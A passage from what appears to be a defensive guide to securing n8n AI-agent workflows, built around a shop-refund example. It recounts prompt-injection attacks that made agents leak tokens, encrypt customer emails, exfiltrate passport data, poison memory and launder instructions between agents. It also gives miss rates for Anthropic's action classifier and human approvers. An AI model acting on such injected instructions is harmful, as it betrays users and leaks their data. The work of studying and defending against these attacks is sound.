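In TrendAI's *Pwning Agentic AI Part I*, Park calls this kind of attack "return-to-tool" and defines it as a prompt injection that makes an agent use its authorised tools against the party it serves. The name recalls return-oriented programming, an older technique in which an attacker strings together pieces of code that a program already contains.

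TrendAI's *Pwning Agentic AI Part II* reports three tests. In the first, an agent read support tickets from a database through a connector meant to be read-only. A ticket led it to read the authentication tokens and post them in the comments, where the customer could see them. The connector ran the agent's SQL inside a read-only transaction but accepted several statements at once, so the agent could end that transaction and start another without the restriction. Supabase now uses a database user without write permission for its own read-only mode, which is more reliable.

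The vulnerable connector had more than 100,000 downloads. Datadog, a monitoring company, had published the flaw in August 2025, and Docker removed the connector from its library after TrendAI reported it in January 2026. The test is slightly odd, though, because the agent's job included posting comments. A real agent with that job would need permission to post them, so an attacker wouldn't need the flaw.

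In the second test, an agent ran on a schedule to give each new ticket a priority. One ticket led it to encrypt every customer's email address with a password the attacker supplied. The agent then set the ticket's priority as usual, and its final message mentioned only that. The attack broke every login that depended on an email address. A backup or the database's own log might allow recovery, but anyone who relied on the agent's summary would not have known anything was wrong.

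The third test most closely resembles an extraction workflow in n8n. A program converted passport images to text, and an agent copied the name, number and other fields into a database. Hidden text in one passport led the agent to copy other customers' details into that passport's "authority" field. The system then displayed the record to the attacker for confirmation, as it did for every customer. Writing to a field that a customer can read is like sending that customer a message, so a builder should treat it as cautiously as sending an email.

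TrendAI ran the passport test with 200 different texts on each of 13 models, or 2,600 runs in total. Most of the large vendors had at least one model that leaked some data at least once, which is a low bar with 200 attempts per model. TrendAI reproduced the encryption attack on six models, all older ones such as GPT-4o and Claude Opus 4.1. It also built all three systems itself and sells security products. The tests are good evidence that such attacks can work with ordinary tools, but they don't show much about how likely an attack is to succeed against a current model.

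AppOmni, also a security company, found a related problem in a commercial product, ServiceNow's Now Assist. A user with few permissions wrote a ticket, and an administrator asked an agent to categorise it. The agent enlisted a second agent, which read a ticket that the user couldn't open and copied its contents into the user's own ticket. By default, these agents have the permissions of the person who starts them, even when someone else wrote the text they read. ServiceNow told AppOmni that this behaviour was intended, and it clarified its documentation.

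### Text that waits in agent memory

An agent's memory can carry text from one run to another without a database column that anyone inspects. *MemoryDojo* (2026), a benchmark of such attacks, describes the process with two formulas:

Mₜ = U(Mₜ₋₁, τₜ)

cₜ = ρ(Mₜ₋₁, xₜ)

Here τₜ is everything that happens in session t, and U is the step that updates the memory M afterwards. When the next task x arrives, ρ selects the stored text c that goes into the model's context. The attacker inserts text into one tool result and changes nothing after that. Since each memory is built from the one before, the text can affect any later session until an update removes it.

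In the session where the attack begins, the only visible effect may be a new memory entry, and such entries are normal. *Hidden in Memory* (2026) describes an attack in which the injected text hijacks only the tool call that writes to memory, and the entry takes effect in a later session. A test that checks each run separately would therefore miss the attack. *From Untrusted Input to Trusted Memory* (2026) finds that existing defences against prompt injection only partly cover such attacks.

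The memory's settings determine which conversations the text reaches. n8n's memory nodes group messages under a session key. If the shop uses the customer's number as the key, text from customer 417 returns only in that customer's later conversations. If the builder types in a fixed key, the same text also enters the context when customer 418 writes. Tang and colleagues found 696 configurations with a chat model, memory and tools, about 8% of those they counted, but didn't examine their keys.

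Gudur asked on n8n's forum, in *Feature Request*, for a feature that scans text before an agent stores it in memory. A respondent mentioned n8n's existing filters and human review, but found no built-in check of this kind in the documentation.

### Whether a warning survives storage

Builders can mark outside text in the prompt, for example by adding a sentence before the customer's email that tells the model not to follow instructions in the email. The model's summary won't normally repeat this warning, and the notes column stores only the summary. If the database records who wrote the note, it records the first workflow's role, so the customer's claim looks like the shop's own information.

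Supabase's wrapper doesn't have this problem, because the server adds the warning each time an agent reads a result. But it adds the same warning to every result, no matter who wrote the content. The shop's second agent is supposed to act on the notes, so a general warning against following them would conflict with its job.

For the second workflow to recognise the customer's claim, the shop would have to store more than the text:

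```json
{
  "order_id": 8812,
  "note": "Lamp arrived broken. Refund of 160 euros agreed by phone.",
  "produced_by": "model",
  "sources": ["email-5521"],
  "outside_authors": ["customer 417"],
  "run": "summary-20914",
  "confirmed_by": null
}
```

The sources should include everything in the model's context when it wrote the note, because any of it could have influenced the wording. If any source comes from outside, the whole note counts as outside text until an employee confirms it. The run number lets the shop find other records from the same run after an attack. The workflow has to use expressions to fill in all of these fields except the note, because an email could otherwise cause the model to write that a manager had confirmed the refund.

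TrendAI recommends logging every tool call together with the content that triggered it. In the shop's second workflow, that content is the note, so the log would not lead back to the original email unless the note includes that email's number.

The second workflow also needs a rule for using this information. A commenter on Hacker News proposed that an agent that reads a user's text should keep only the permissions that user also has. Taken literally, this would stop every refund, because customer 417 has no permission to issue one. The shop would instead have to define what a customer may request, such as a refund of up to the purchase price on their own order. The note could then lead to a payment of 80 euros but not 160.

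Each value in a record needs its own label. In a support database, almost every note comes from a customer, while the price in the same row comes from the shop's checkout and remains reliable. Labelling whole records would work poorly, because blocking refunds for any order with outside text would block nearly all refunds.

Memory systems make this harder. *When Agents Remember Too Much* (2026) notes that some summarise entries or merge new details into old ones. If an entry began as an employee's instruction and later absorbed a sentence from customer 417, its original label would be wrong. The system would have to update the sources at every merge. It would also lose the sources whenever text leaves the shop, for example when a supplier's helpdesk turns the shop's email into a ticket.

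## Checks before a call runs: schemas, rules, filters and human review

A workflow that has lost track of where a value came from can still test the value before acting on it. Take a simple mistake. Customer 417 writes that the lamp from order 8812 arrived broken, and the model adds a zero to the price:

`{ "order_id": 8812, "amount": 800 }`

The shop could put several kinds of check between this call and the refund service:

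| Check | Result for this call | A wrong call that would still pass |
|---|---|---|
| Schema with two numbers | passes | any amount on any order |
| Lists of permitted values | fails, if one of the lists covers amounts | 45 euros on order 8812 |
| Rule that uses the orders table | fails | 45 euros on order 8813 |
| Classifier or second model | probably passes, unless it sees the price | hard to predict |
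| Human review | depends on what the reviewer sees | anything the reviewer overlooks |

It is tempting to assume that a call that has passed its checks is the call the shop wanted. But a check only removes some of the calls that the node could make. If R is the set of all those calls and Aᵢ is the set that the i-th check accepts, a call that passes n checks lies in

R ∩ A₁ ∩ … ∩ Aₙ

The assumption is safe only if this set contains only the intended call. The shop's refund tool allows a billion possible refunds before any checks are applied, so the checks have many to rule out.

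Even a single remaining call might be wrong. If customer 417 asked for a new lamp instead of money, the shop shouldn't make a refund, and no check on the order number and amount can detect that mistake.

### Schemas and types

*Try, Check and Retry* (2026), which describes a method for improving tool calls, uses a typical schema check. Fixed rules test the tool's name, the arguments and their types. The refund of 800 euros would pass these rules, and so would one of 80 euros.

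A schema check therefore confirms that a call has the right form. It stops many malformed values before a request leaves n8n, but it doesn't rule out any of the billion possible refunds.

JSON Schema, the standard format for such descriptions, can also set a maximum for a number, but `$fromAI()` has no argument for one. A builder can write "at most 500 euros" in the description, but that is only a hint to the model. Even an enforced maximum would be a crude check. A shop that sells lamps for 80 euros and sofas for 900 has to allow refunds of up to 900 euros, so an 800-euro refund for a lamp would pass.

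### Lists of permitted values

A list of allowed values works well for a field that has only a few, such as a currency or a ticket category. The list for the order number has to depend on the customer, so the workflow can look up customer 417's orders before the agent starts and permit only 8812 and 8813.

This list allows the bad refund because its order number is correct. A second list that permits only the amounts 80 and 45 would stop it. But the two lists would still accept a refund of 45 euros on order 8812, because each value is on its own list. To prevent that, the shop would need a list of permitted pairs of order number and amount, which is close to a rule that reads the orders table.

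In a workflow without an agent, the builder can put such a check in an IF node between the model and the refund node. An agent has no ordinary connection to its tools, so there is nowhere to insert the IF node. The builder can instead make the tool a separate small workflow. The model fills in the order number and the amount, and the small workflow tests them and posts the refund only if they pass.

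If the test fails, the small workflow can return an error to the model, which may try again with other values. The wording of the error can affect those values. For example, "The highest possible refund is 80 euros" could lead the model to request 80 euros for a scratch that warrants only 10.

### Rules that use trusted data

The most useful check for the shop compares the call with its own records. Suppose the orders table has a `refunded` column with the amount already paid back on each order. The small workflow could run this statement before it contacts the refund service:

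```sql
WITH proposed AS (
  SELECT $1::int AS id, $2::int AS customer, $3::numeric AS amount
)
UPDATE orders SET refunded = orders.refunded + proposed.amount
FROM proposed
WHERE orders.id = proposed.id
  AND orders.customer_id = proposed.customer
  AND proposed.amount > 0
  AND orders.refunded + proposed.amount <= orders.price
RETURNING orders.id
```

The model supplies the order number and the amount, and the workflow supplies the customer number from its own lookup. The `SELECT` line uses each placeholder once and in ascending order because n8n users have had trouble with placeholders.

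For the bad refund, the last condition compares 800 with 80 and fails, so the statement returns nothing and the workflow stops. A refund of 80 euros returns the order number, and the table records it as paid. Because the same statement checks and records the refund, an agent that makes the same call twice in quick succession can't refund the order twice. The second statement waits for the first, then returns nothing because there is no money left to refund. If the refund service later rejects the request, the workflow has to subtract the amount from the recorded refunds, or customer 417 will never get the money.

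The condition `amount > 0` is easy to forget. Without it, a refund of minus 80 euros would pass the check, and some payment services might treat it as a charge.

This rule checks that the order belongs to the customer and that the refunds on it don't exceed its price. It leaves 8,000 possible amounts on order 8812 and 4,500 on order 8813, for a total of 12,500 possible refunds instead of a billion. If the shop gives only full refunds, the rule can require the exact price, which leaves two possible refunds, one for each order. The orders table can't show which order customer 417 means by "my last order".

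The rule can fail if the stored price and the refund amount are in different units. If the table stores prices in cents, the price of the lamp is 8000. The bad refund of 800 then passes because it is less than 8000, and a service that counts in euros pays out 800 euros. A builder can find this fault by testing the check with this call before relying on it.

Sometimes a check has no trusted value to compare the model's output with. In the invoice template that Tang and colleagues describe, software converts each uploaded invoice to text before the model extracts the amounts. The workflow then cleans up the JSON, converts the numbers to a standard format, removes duplicates and compares the invoice with the records in a Notion database. In ambiguous cases, it asks a person on Slack whether to record the invoice as paid or unpaid, or to archive it. But if the conversion to text turns 80 euros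 into 800 on a new invoice, every automatic check may pass, because the database has no earlier record of that amount.

### Classifiers and second models

A builder may also use another model to check whether a call looks right. n8n's *Guardrails* describes a node that checks text before it goes to a model or checks the text the model returns. The node can look for blocked keywords, secret keys, web addresses, personal data, patterns the builder defines, attempts to get around a model's safety rules, or a change of subject. Some of these checks use fixed patterns and others use a model.

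The refund call contains no blocked word, web address or personal data, so it would pass most of these checks. A pattern that matches amounts with three or more digits would stop it, but would also stop every legitimate refund of 100 euros or more. None of the node's listed checks compares a value with a database record, though the builder can write a prompt for a custom check.

What a Guardrails node can check also depends on its position. If it runs before the agent, it checks the customer's email. It can check the final answer if it runs after the agent, but by then the agent has already called its tools and the refund has gone out. To check the refund call before it runs, the node would have to be inside the tool's own workflow.

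The settings need testing. If the builder has the node look for every type of personal data, many ordinary emails will go to the Fail branch because customers sign with their phone numbers. n8n's explanation of the threshold is also confusing. It defines the threshold as the confidence the model needs to flag a text, which means a higher threshold should flag fewer texts, but it calls a higher threshold stricter.

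A second model can judge the call itself instead of looking for forbidden text. *Gecko* (2026), a simulated environment for testing tool calls, has a model compare each argument with the tool's description. The model checks formats and uses common sense about ranges, so it would reject 30 as the hour of the day. It is instructed to accept a value when it is unsure. It would probably accept a refund of 800 euros, because some refunds are that large.

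A second model can detect the mistake only if the builder gives it the lamp's price. A rule in code can use the same price, and it returns the same result every time. A second model is more useful for questions that can't be answered from the orders table, such as whether the sender is asking for money or a new lamp.

Anthropic has measured a check of this kind in its coding agent, Claude Code. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes a classifier that examines risky actions before they run. A fast first stage either lets the action through or flags it, and a slower second stage reconsiders the flagged ones. Anthropic tested the classifier on 10,000 ordinary tool calls by its employees and on 52 real cases in which the agent had gone further than the user wanted:

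| | Ordinary calls blocked by mistake | Overeager actions missed |
|---|---|---|
| First stage only | 8.5% | 6.6% |
| Both stages | 0.4% | 17% |

With only 52 cases, the true miss rate could plausibly be anywhere from about 9% to 30%. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier recognised the danger but wrongly concluded that the user had agreed to the action. For example, one user had asked the agent to clean up a proposed code change, but that request did not cover overwriting the project's history.

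The design would suit the shop less well. The classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the results of those calls, so that injected text in the results can't influence it. Anthropic acknowledges that the classifier therefore can't distinguish a job number the agent looked up from one it made up. In the shop, it wouldn't receive the database result with the price of 80 euros. It also uses the user's messages to determine what the agent may do. If the shop passed customer emails to it as user messages, an attacker could write an email that both requests a harmful action and authorizes it.

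Filters for prompt injection stop many attacks, but attackers who keep adapting their texts still get some through. Langflow, another node-based platform, warns that its model-based checks can miss violations and shouldn't be the only safeguard.

### How n8n asks a person

In *Confirmations/Approvals for Tool use*, CodeZeno wanted users to see and confirm an email before an agent sent it. n8n had nodes that wait for a person's answer, but CodeZeno couldn't place one between an agent and its tool. n8n announced a way to do this for version 2.6 in *New human-in-the-loop capabilities add fine-grained control*.

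The builder adds a review step to the agent and connects the risky tools to it. Other tools can run without review, so the shop could require approval for refunds but not for database searches. n8n's *Human-in-the-loop for tools* sets out what happens next:

1. The model proposes a call to a tool that requires review.
2. The workflow pauses and sends a request to the reviewer.
3. The reviewer approves or denies the call.
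4. After an approval, the tool runs with the values that the model supplied. After a denial, it doesn't run, and the model learns of the rejection.

The request can go through n8n's own chat, Slack, Discord, Telegram, Microsoft Teams, Gmail, WhatsApp, Google Chat or Microsoft Outlook, and it doesn't have to use the same channel as the customer. n8n recommends explaining the review in the agent's instructions so that the model responds appropriately to a denial. Without that explanation, the agent might tell customer 417 that the denied refund is on its way.

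The pause for human approval is a much stronger safeguard than a prompt that tells the model to ask first, because n8n enforces the pause. An injected email can cause the model to propose a refund, but the refund runs only if a person approves it.

### What the reviewer doesn't see

The builder writes the message that the reviewer receives. Two variables are available for it. `$tool.name` is the name of the node on the canvas, and `$tool.parameters` contains the parameters of the proposed call, including the fields that the model fills in through `$fromAI()`. In n8n's example message, the refund would look roughly like this:

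```
Tool: refund_order
{
  "order_id": 8812,
  "amount": 800
}
```

A reviewer who doesn't know the price has no reason to object. The message is accurate, but the number 80 doesn't appear in it.

Some messages contain even less. In one of n8n's examples, an agent sends contracts to customers. The approval request, as n8n describes it, shows only the tool's name above the two buttons, so the reviewer approves a contract without seeing the deal number or the email address.

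The fields that the builder has fixed are also missing, because they aren't part of the tool's input schema. Suppose a Postgres tool named "Update orders" contains this query:

`UPDATE orders SET status = 'cancelled' WHERE ordered_on < $1`

The model fills in the date, and the reviewer sees `{ "date": "2026-03-01" }`. The message doesn't show that the query cancels orders, or whether it will cancel three or 4,000. A better node name would help make clear that the query cancels orders. To show how many, the workflow has to count the rows with a separate query before requesting approval.

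deeKay93 ran into the same difficulty in the discussion below n8n's announcement. To delete an email, the model passes only the email's id, but the person who approves the deletion needs the subject and the sender. The model could write a description, but it might describe the wrong email. A reply recommended fetching the email with an ordinary node before the approval step, and deeKay93 had also pointed out that data retrieved without the model can't get mixed up.

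The shop could do this by letting the agent only propose refunds. Ordinary nodes would then look up the order and send the request:

```
Customer 417: "The lamp arrived broken."
Order 8812: lamp, price 80 euros, refunded so far 0 euros
Proposed refund: 800 euros
```

Only the last number and the choice of order come from the model, and the mistake is now easy to see. n8n likewise advises builders to show the original email next to the model's output. A false claim in the email, such as that a manager has agreed to 800 euros, can mislead the reviewer too, so the message should show which lines the customer wrote.

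Approval requests can also time out. n8n suggests a limit of two to four hours for everyday approvals. When the limit passes on one of its nodes that send a message and wait, the workflow continues without any approval data. A workflow that only checks whether the reviewer rejected the refund would then treat no answer as approval. n8n's template for reviewing articles avoids this with separate branches for approval, rejection and no answer, and the no-answer branch notifies a manager.

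An employee might also refund order 8812 by hand while the request is waiting for approval. The rule that compares the refund with the orders table should therefore run after the approval, even if it has already run once.

### What difference the message makes

In *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026) tested how the content of an approval request affects people's decisions. In one scenario, a user asks an agent to send an auditor only the totals from some invoices. Injected text makes the agent copy the individual invoice rows into `report.csv`, and the agent then asks for permission to send that file to the auditor. The recipient is correct and the file name is harmless, so a reviewer has to know how the file was created to see what is wrong.

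They recruited 80 volunteers and gave each of them 12 requests, half of which broke the user's rules. Each person used one of four versions of the approval screen:

| What the reviewer saw | Unsafe requests approved | Legitimate requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
| The exact arguments as well | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| Also the user's rules and a log of earlier steps | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
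| The same facts, arranged around the consequence | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

An approval request that gives only the tool's name resembles the first version, and one that prints `$tool.parameters` resembles the second. Adding the rules and the history reduced unsafe approvals further, which supports including the order's price in the shop's message.

The advantage of the last version over the third is uncertain. After Hossain and colleagues adjusted for other factors, the last version had 7.9 percentage points fewer unsafe approvals, with a 95% interval from 19.7 points fewer to 3.8 points more. They hadn't registered their analysis in advance, and each version had only 20 participants.

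The volunteers also faced an unsafe request half the time. A shop employee might see one wrong refund in a hundred, and people who rarely find errors tend to stop looking for them.

### Approval fatigue

Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users approve 97% of permission requests (an earlier figure was 93%). Most of the requests are probably harmless, so the rate alone doesn't prove that people have stopped reading them. But the same users reject 39% of the agent's plans, which suggests that they pay more attention to plans than to permission requests.

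Anthropic also commissioned a controlled test, for which an outside firm hired 1,053 professional testers for what they understood to be a coding study. At some point in each session, the study replaced the text of one permission request with a clearly dangerous command. Of the testers, 143 (13.6%) refused it. The refusal rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more requests. Anthropic's classifier blocked 89% of the same commands, and its rate didn't fall in longer sessions.

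These figures come from Anthropic, which was explaining why it had replaced most permission requests with its own classifier. The testers weren't working on their own projects, so they had less to lose than a shop with its own money at stake. The fall from 17% to 5% still matters to the shop because it suggests that each additional request makes the others less effective. Anthropic still recommends that people review important changes to production systems.

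*Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of problems with agents that work on users' files. User review played a part in 105 of them. In 80, the user had set the agent to run without asking for approval, often to avoid hundreds of requests per session. In 31, the request had shown a command but not what it would do to the files. According to *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of how software practitioners make these decisions, people who keep approving requests may do so from habit, fatigue or pressure to finish their work, rather than because they trust the agent more.

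This makes approval rates a poor measure of whether a workflow still needs review. n8n advises that if a reviewer approves 99% of a workflow's outputs, the builder can probably replace the review with occasional checks. Suppose the shop's agent proposes 1,000 refunds, of which ten are wrong. A perfect reviewer rejects those ten and approves 99%. A reviewer as inattentive as Anthropic's testers rejects one or two of them and approves more than 99.8%. By n8n's rule, the shop would drop the review in both cases, although the perfect reviewer prevents ten wrong payments.

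The shop can test its reviewers the way Anthropic did, by occasionally inserting a wrong refund that the workflow won't carry out. It can also send them fewer refunds to review. If the rule in code has already rejected impossible amounts, employees need to see only unusual cases, such as refunds above 100 euros or emails that mention a phone call. In a similar example from n8n, only expenses above 1,000 dollars go to a manager.

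n8n also suggests combining many requests into one message with buttons for each. That means fewer interruptions, but 50 refunds in a row are an invitation to click through them.

### How often builders include checks

Tang and colleagues provide the only broad count of such checks in n8n workflows. For each of their 6,003 public templates, they started at every model node and followed the connections for up to six steps to see whether the output reached a node with an external action. They then gave each template one label:

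| Route from the model to an external action | Templates | Share |
|---|---|---|
| Through at least one logic or validation node | 2,509 | 41.80% |
| Without such a node or a person in between | 1,592 | 26.52% |
| Through a person's approval | 167 | 2.78% |
| No route found | 1,363 | 22.71% |
| No model node that the program could trace | 372 | 6.20% |

Model output reaches an external action in 4,268 of the templates, and about 4% of those require a person to approve it.

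The first row includes templates whose logic nodes don't check anything. For example, a Switch node that sends complaints to one department and orders to another would put a template in this group, even if the workflow then pays any refund the model proposes. So 41.80% is an upper limit on the share of templates with a logic node that tests the model's output, and the real share could be much lower.

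Each template has only one label, and human approval takes precedence over logic nodes, which take precedence over direct routes. A template in which a person approves one email but the model sends five others directly counts as having human approval, and one with a single route through an IF node and several direct routes counts in the first row. The share of templates with at least one direct route is therefore probably higher than 26.52%.

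Tang and colleagues also found error handling in 1,829 templates (30%). They traced the connections backwards from each error setting until they reached a model, a tool or another error handler, to see whether the error handling was related to a model. In 684 templates (11%), at least one trace ended at a model. The error setting in these templates often followed a step that converts or tests the model's output, so some builders expect badly formed answers.

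But error handling starts only when a node reports an error. If the refund service accepts the 800-euro refund, no error occurs, so one of the 684 templates could still pay it without delay.

Like the other template counts, these figures describe designs, not running workflows. The researchers looked for specific signs of human approval, such as the words "wait for approval", and may have missed approval steps with other names. They checked 200 templates by hand and found that their program had traced the routes correctly.

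The count has a larger gap for agents. Tang and colleagues traced the routes to external actions through the execution graph, which seems to leave out the connections between agents and their tools, although they don't say so explicitly for this part of the study. That omission would also affect the count of steps added with n8n's newer review feature, because those steps sit on the same connections.

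In the shop's workflow, everything that acts is attached to the agent as a tool, so no ordinary node follows the agent. The program would probably find no route to an external action and put the workflow among the 1,363 templates in the fourth row, which Tang and colleagues label "low autonomy", even though the agent can refund 800 euros without human approval.

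## Designs that limit what a model-filled value can do

The builder can redesign the shop's tool so that the model can't request most of the billion refunds it currently allows, instead of checking each one. For example, if the tool has no field for the amount, the model can't enter an amount with an extra zero.

*Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* recommends this approach for agents in general. Its patterns restrict an agent so tightly that it can no longer solve arbitrary tasks, which the paper considers a reasonable trade-off for the added security. A shop that mainly looks up orders, pays refunds and answers emails may lose little from this restriction.

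### A refund tool with one open field

A builder who makes the refund tool a separate small workflow, as for the earlier checks, can also fix its operation, its target and most of its values. The shop's new refund tool takes a single value from the model:

`{ "order_id": 8812 }`

The small workflow then runs this statement:

```sql
UPDATE orders SET refunded = price
WHERE id = $1 AND customer_id = $2 AND refunded = 0
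RETURNING id, price AS amount
```

The model supplies the order number, and the workflow supplies the customer number. If the statement returns a row, an HTTP Request node copies the id and the amount from it and posts them to the refund service. If order 8812 belongs to someone else or already has a refund, the statement returns nothing and the workflow ends. (If the refund service rejects the request, the workflow has to set `refunded` back to 0.)

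This tool can't pay partial refunds. A customer with a scratched lamp has to wait for an employee, unless the shop adds a second tool that always pays 10 euros for minor damage.

Narrow tools can also replace model-written SQL. In *Using AI Agents to query and analyze project data securely in n8n*, a forum user wanted a bot to turn questions about projects into database queries. The user didn't trust the agent to write safe SQL, so one idea was to give it a separate workflow that validates the query and fetches the data.

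The two sample questions in the thread are which tasks are left for today and which are unfinished. The bot could answer both using two tools with fixed queries, and there would be no SQL to validate. But it couldn't answer a question that nobody had written a query for.

### Identity from the trigger

The refund statement protects other customers only if the customer number is right. If the model filled it in, an email claiming to come from customer 418 could give the sender access to that customer's orders. The builder should therefore use an expression:

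`{{ $('Find customer').item.json.customer_id }}`

"Find customer" is a Postgres node that runs before the agent and looks up the sender's address in the customer table. The model can't change its result. The builder should test this with two emails in the same run, in case the tool uses the first sender's number for both.

Someone could defeat this lookup by forging the sender's address. Costa, Köpf and colleagues at Microsoft point out in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (2025) that mail servers can authenticate sender addresses with DMARC. Under it, the owner of a domain publishes a policy, and the receiving server checks whether the message came from a server that may send for that domain.

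The receiving server normally records the outcome in a header, which the shop's workflow can read before it looks up the customer. The workflow should trust only the header that the shop's own mail server added, because a forger can include a fake one. If the check fails or the domain has no policy, the agent can still answer general questions but shouldn't have access to orders.

DMARC authenticates only the sender's domain, so the shop relies on the email provider to stop one user from writing under another's address. Someone who has broken into customer 417's mailbox also passes the check. A form that requires customers to log in to the shop gives better proof, because the login identifies the customer.

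### A model that proposes and a workflow that commits

With the new tool, the agent still decides whether and when to issue a refund. The builder can take that decision away too by having the model return a proposal:

`{ "order_id": 8812, "request": "refund" }`

The second field accepts only "refund", "replacement" or "question". Ordinary nodes then look up the order, apply the shop's limits and carry out the action. For a replacement, the workflow can create a warehouse task without calling the refund service.

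In the invoice template that Tang and colleagues describe, code writes the result of a comparison with existing records to a field named `next_action`, and a Switch node uses that field to choose the branch. A wrong amount from the model can still send the workflow down the wrong branch, but only one that the builder created.

This design also prevents false confirmations, because the workflow can fill in a fixed sentence, such as "We have refunded 80 euros for order 8812", after the refund service confirms the payment.

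### Separate models for reading and acting

*The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) proposes dividing an assistant between two models. A privileged model can use tools, and only a quarantined model, which has no tools, reads outside text. The privileged model refers to the quarantined model's output by a name such as `$email-summary-1`, and ordinary software inserts the text later.

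Whether separating reading from acting helps depends on what passes between the two models. The shop's two workflows in the section on messages and records were also separated this way, but the second still paid 160 euros because a free-text note passed it the customer's claim from the first.

Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues call this kind of failure "boundary laundering" in *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026). They built a system in which one agent queried a database, another sent notifications and a third coordinated them. All three ran GPT-5.2 with CaMeL, a defence against prompt injection described below. They planted an instruction in the database to send the data to an outside address, then asked the system to send a summary of job applicants to Julie on Slack.

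The database agent and the coordinator kept to their plans. But the coordinator included the summary in its request to the notification agent, which treated the whole request as coming from its user. The notification agent sent the Slack message and then emailed the applicants' data to the outside address.

The remedy was to send instructions and data between agents through separate channels. In a multi-agent benchmark, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL on each agent and 0.0% with the separate channels. Boundary laundering therefore seems rare in that benchmark, although the demonstration shows it can happen. The forum user's other idea, two agents in one n8n workflow, has the same kind of boundary.

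The shop can avoid passing free text across the boundary. Suppose the reading model passes on only an order number, which the workflow accepts if it is 8812 or 8813, and one of the three request types. An email can then affect which of six combinations reaches the acting part, but it cannot pass on an instruction. Costa and colleagues' system, FIDES, uses the same idea and ranks output types by how much information they can carry. A yes-or-no answer carries one bit, a choice from a list carries slightly more, and free text has no such limit.

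### Caps and actions that the shop can undo

Taking the amount from the orders table caps each refund at the order's price, but it doesn't limit the shop's total loss. If the shop had 10,000 orders averaging 60 euros, someone who could forge every customer's address could trigger 600,000 euros in refunds.

A rate cap limits that loss. The shop could store the amount left for the day's automatic refunds in a database row that resets to 2,000 euros each morning. The refund tool subtracts each payment from this amount and stops when too little is left, and employees handle the remaining refunds. An attacker could deliberately use up the budget and make honest customers wait, so a smaller limit per customer is also useful.

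The number of rows a tool can read or change also needs a cap. The order lookup can be limited to 20 rows, and a tool that cancels orders can be built to cancel nothing if its condition matches more than one order. To do this, the tool has to count the matching orders before it changes them, or make the change in a transaction that it can roll back.

Some mistakes matter less if the shop can reverse them. The Gmail template that Tang and colleagues describe saves each reply as a draft, which they note leaves a person in control of whether it is sent. For deletions, the shop can write the current time into a `deleted_at` column, leave the row in place, and have another workflow remove it after 30 days. The shop's other queries must ignore rows with a deletion time, or deleted orders will still appear in reports.

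A payment is harder to reverse, so the shop could hold each refund for an hour to give an employee a chance to cancel it. But a delay or a soft deletion helps only if somebody notices the mistake in time.

### The rebuilt workflow

The shop now verifies the sender, looks up the customer and starts an agent with three narrow tools. The order lookup uses the customer number from the trigger, and the refund tool takes only an order number from the model. The Gmail tool replies to the address in the customer table, and the model writes only the text. (The builder shouldn't copy the recipient from the email, because a Reply-To header can name a different address from the one that the mail server checked.)

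For customer 417, the count of reachable actions changes as follows, if the refund service would accept any amount up to 1,000 euros:

| | Original workflow | Rebuilt workflow |
|---|---|---|
| Orders the agent can read | 10,000 | 2 |
| Orders the agent can refund | 10,000 | 2 |
| Possible refunds in one call | 1 billion | 2 |
| Largest loss | 1,000 euros per call, for any number of calls | 125 euros in total |
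| Possible recipients of a reply | any address | 1 |

The refund tool needs both changes. Binding only the customer number would leave 200,000 possible refunds (100,000 amounts for each of two orders), and fixing only the amount would leave 10,000. The total of 125 euros is the price of both orders, and further emails can't raise it because the statement blocks a second refund on the same order.

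The rebuilt lookup and Gmail tools also prevent injected text from making the agent send customer 418's orders to customer 417. The agent can no longer read customer 418's orders, and its replies go only to the customer whose orders it can read.

These numbers depend on several assumptions, most importantly that the email really comes from customer 417. A forger who gets past the check controls the same two refunds. If the refund service pays only to the original card, the forger gains nothing, but the shop still loses up to 125 euros.

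The prices in the orders table must also be correct and in the unit the refund service uses. No other tool or workflow may let outside text change a price, reset the `refunded` column or replace the address in the customer table. For example, a tool for changing email addresses would undo the protection on the Gmail tool.

The model can still refund order 8813 instead of 8812, or pay a refund when the customer wanted a new lamp. A dishonest customer can also write an injection that makes the agent refund both orders, but might get the same refunds by falsely claiming that both parcels arrived broken.

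### Labels that follow the data

The builder of the rebuilt workflow decided by hand which values may come from outside text. Information-flow control makes such decisions while the system runs. It labels each piece of data with its origin, passes the label on to everything derived from it, and checks the labels before each call. A filter looks for suspicious content, but the survey *From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026) points out that harmless-looking content can also have an influence it shouldn't have.

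CaMeL, from Google DeepMind, adds such labels to the division between a privileged and a quarantined model. Willison (2025) explains in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* that it addresses a flaw in his earlier design. In that design, the quarantined model can't call tools, but an attacker can still make it return the wrong email address, which the privileged model then uses without seeing it.

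In CaMeL, the privileged model turns the user's request into a short program in a restricted form of Python. Suppose an employee of the shop asks the system to refund the order in the latest complaint. The program might look like this:

```python
email = get_latest_email()
order = ask_quarantined_model("Which order is this about?", email)
refund_order(order_id=order)
```

CaMeL's interpreter runs the program and tracks where each value came from. The email comes from outside, so the order number taken from it also counts as outside data. If the shop's policy requires a trusted order number for refunds, the interpreter stops at the last line or asks the employee to approve the refund. The email can change the order number but can't add a fourth line to the program.

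If applied strictly, this policy would block every refund in the shop, because customers always give the order number in an email. It would need an exception for orders that belong to the verified sender, which requires the same lookup as the narrow refund tool. Willison considers the work of writing and maintaining such policies a serious drawback.

In FIDES, from Costa and colleagues, the model plans one step at a time instead of writing the whole program in advance, and it reads trusted results directly. When a tool returns untrusted text, FIDES stores it in a variable and gives the model only the variable's name.

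An integrity label marks data as trusted (T) or untrusted (U), and combining the two produces untrusted data, which FIDES writes as T ⊔ U = U. A confidentiality label can list who may read the data, and only readers listed for every source may read the combined data. For example, if employees and customer 417 may read one order, and employees and customer 418 may read another, only employees may read a summary of both, so the agent couldn't send it to customer 417.

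One FIDES policy lets a call with consequences run only if

ℓ_tool ⊔ ℓ₁ ⊔ … ⊔ ℓₙ = T

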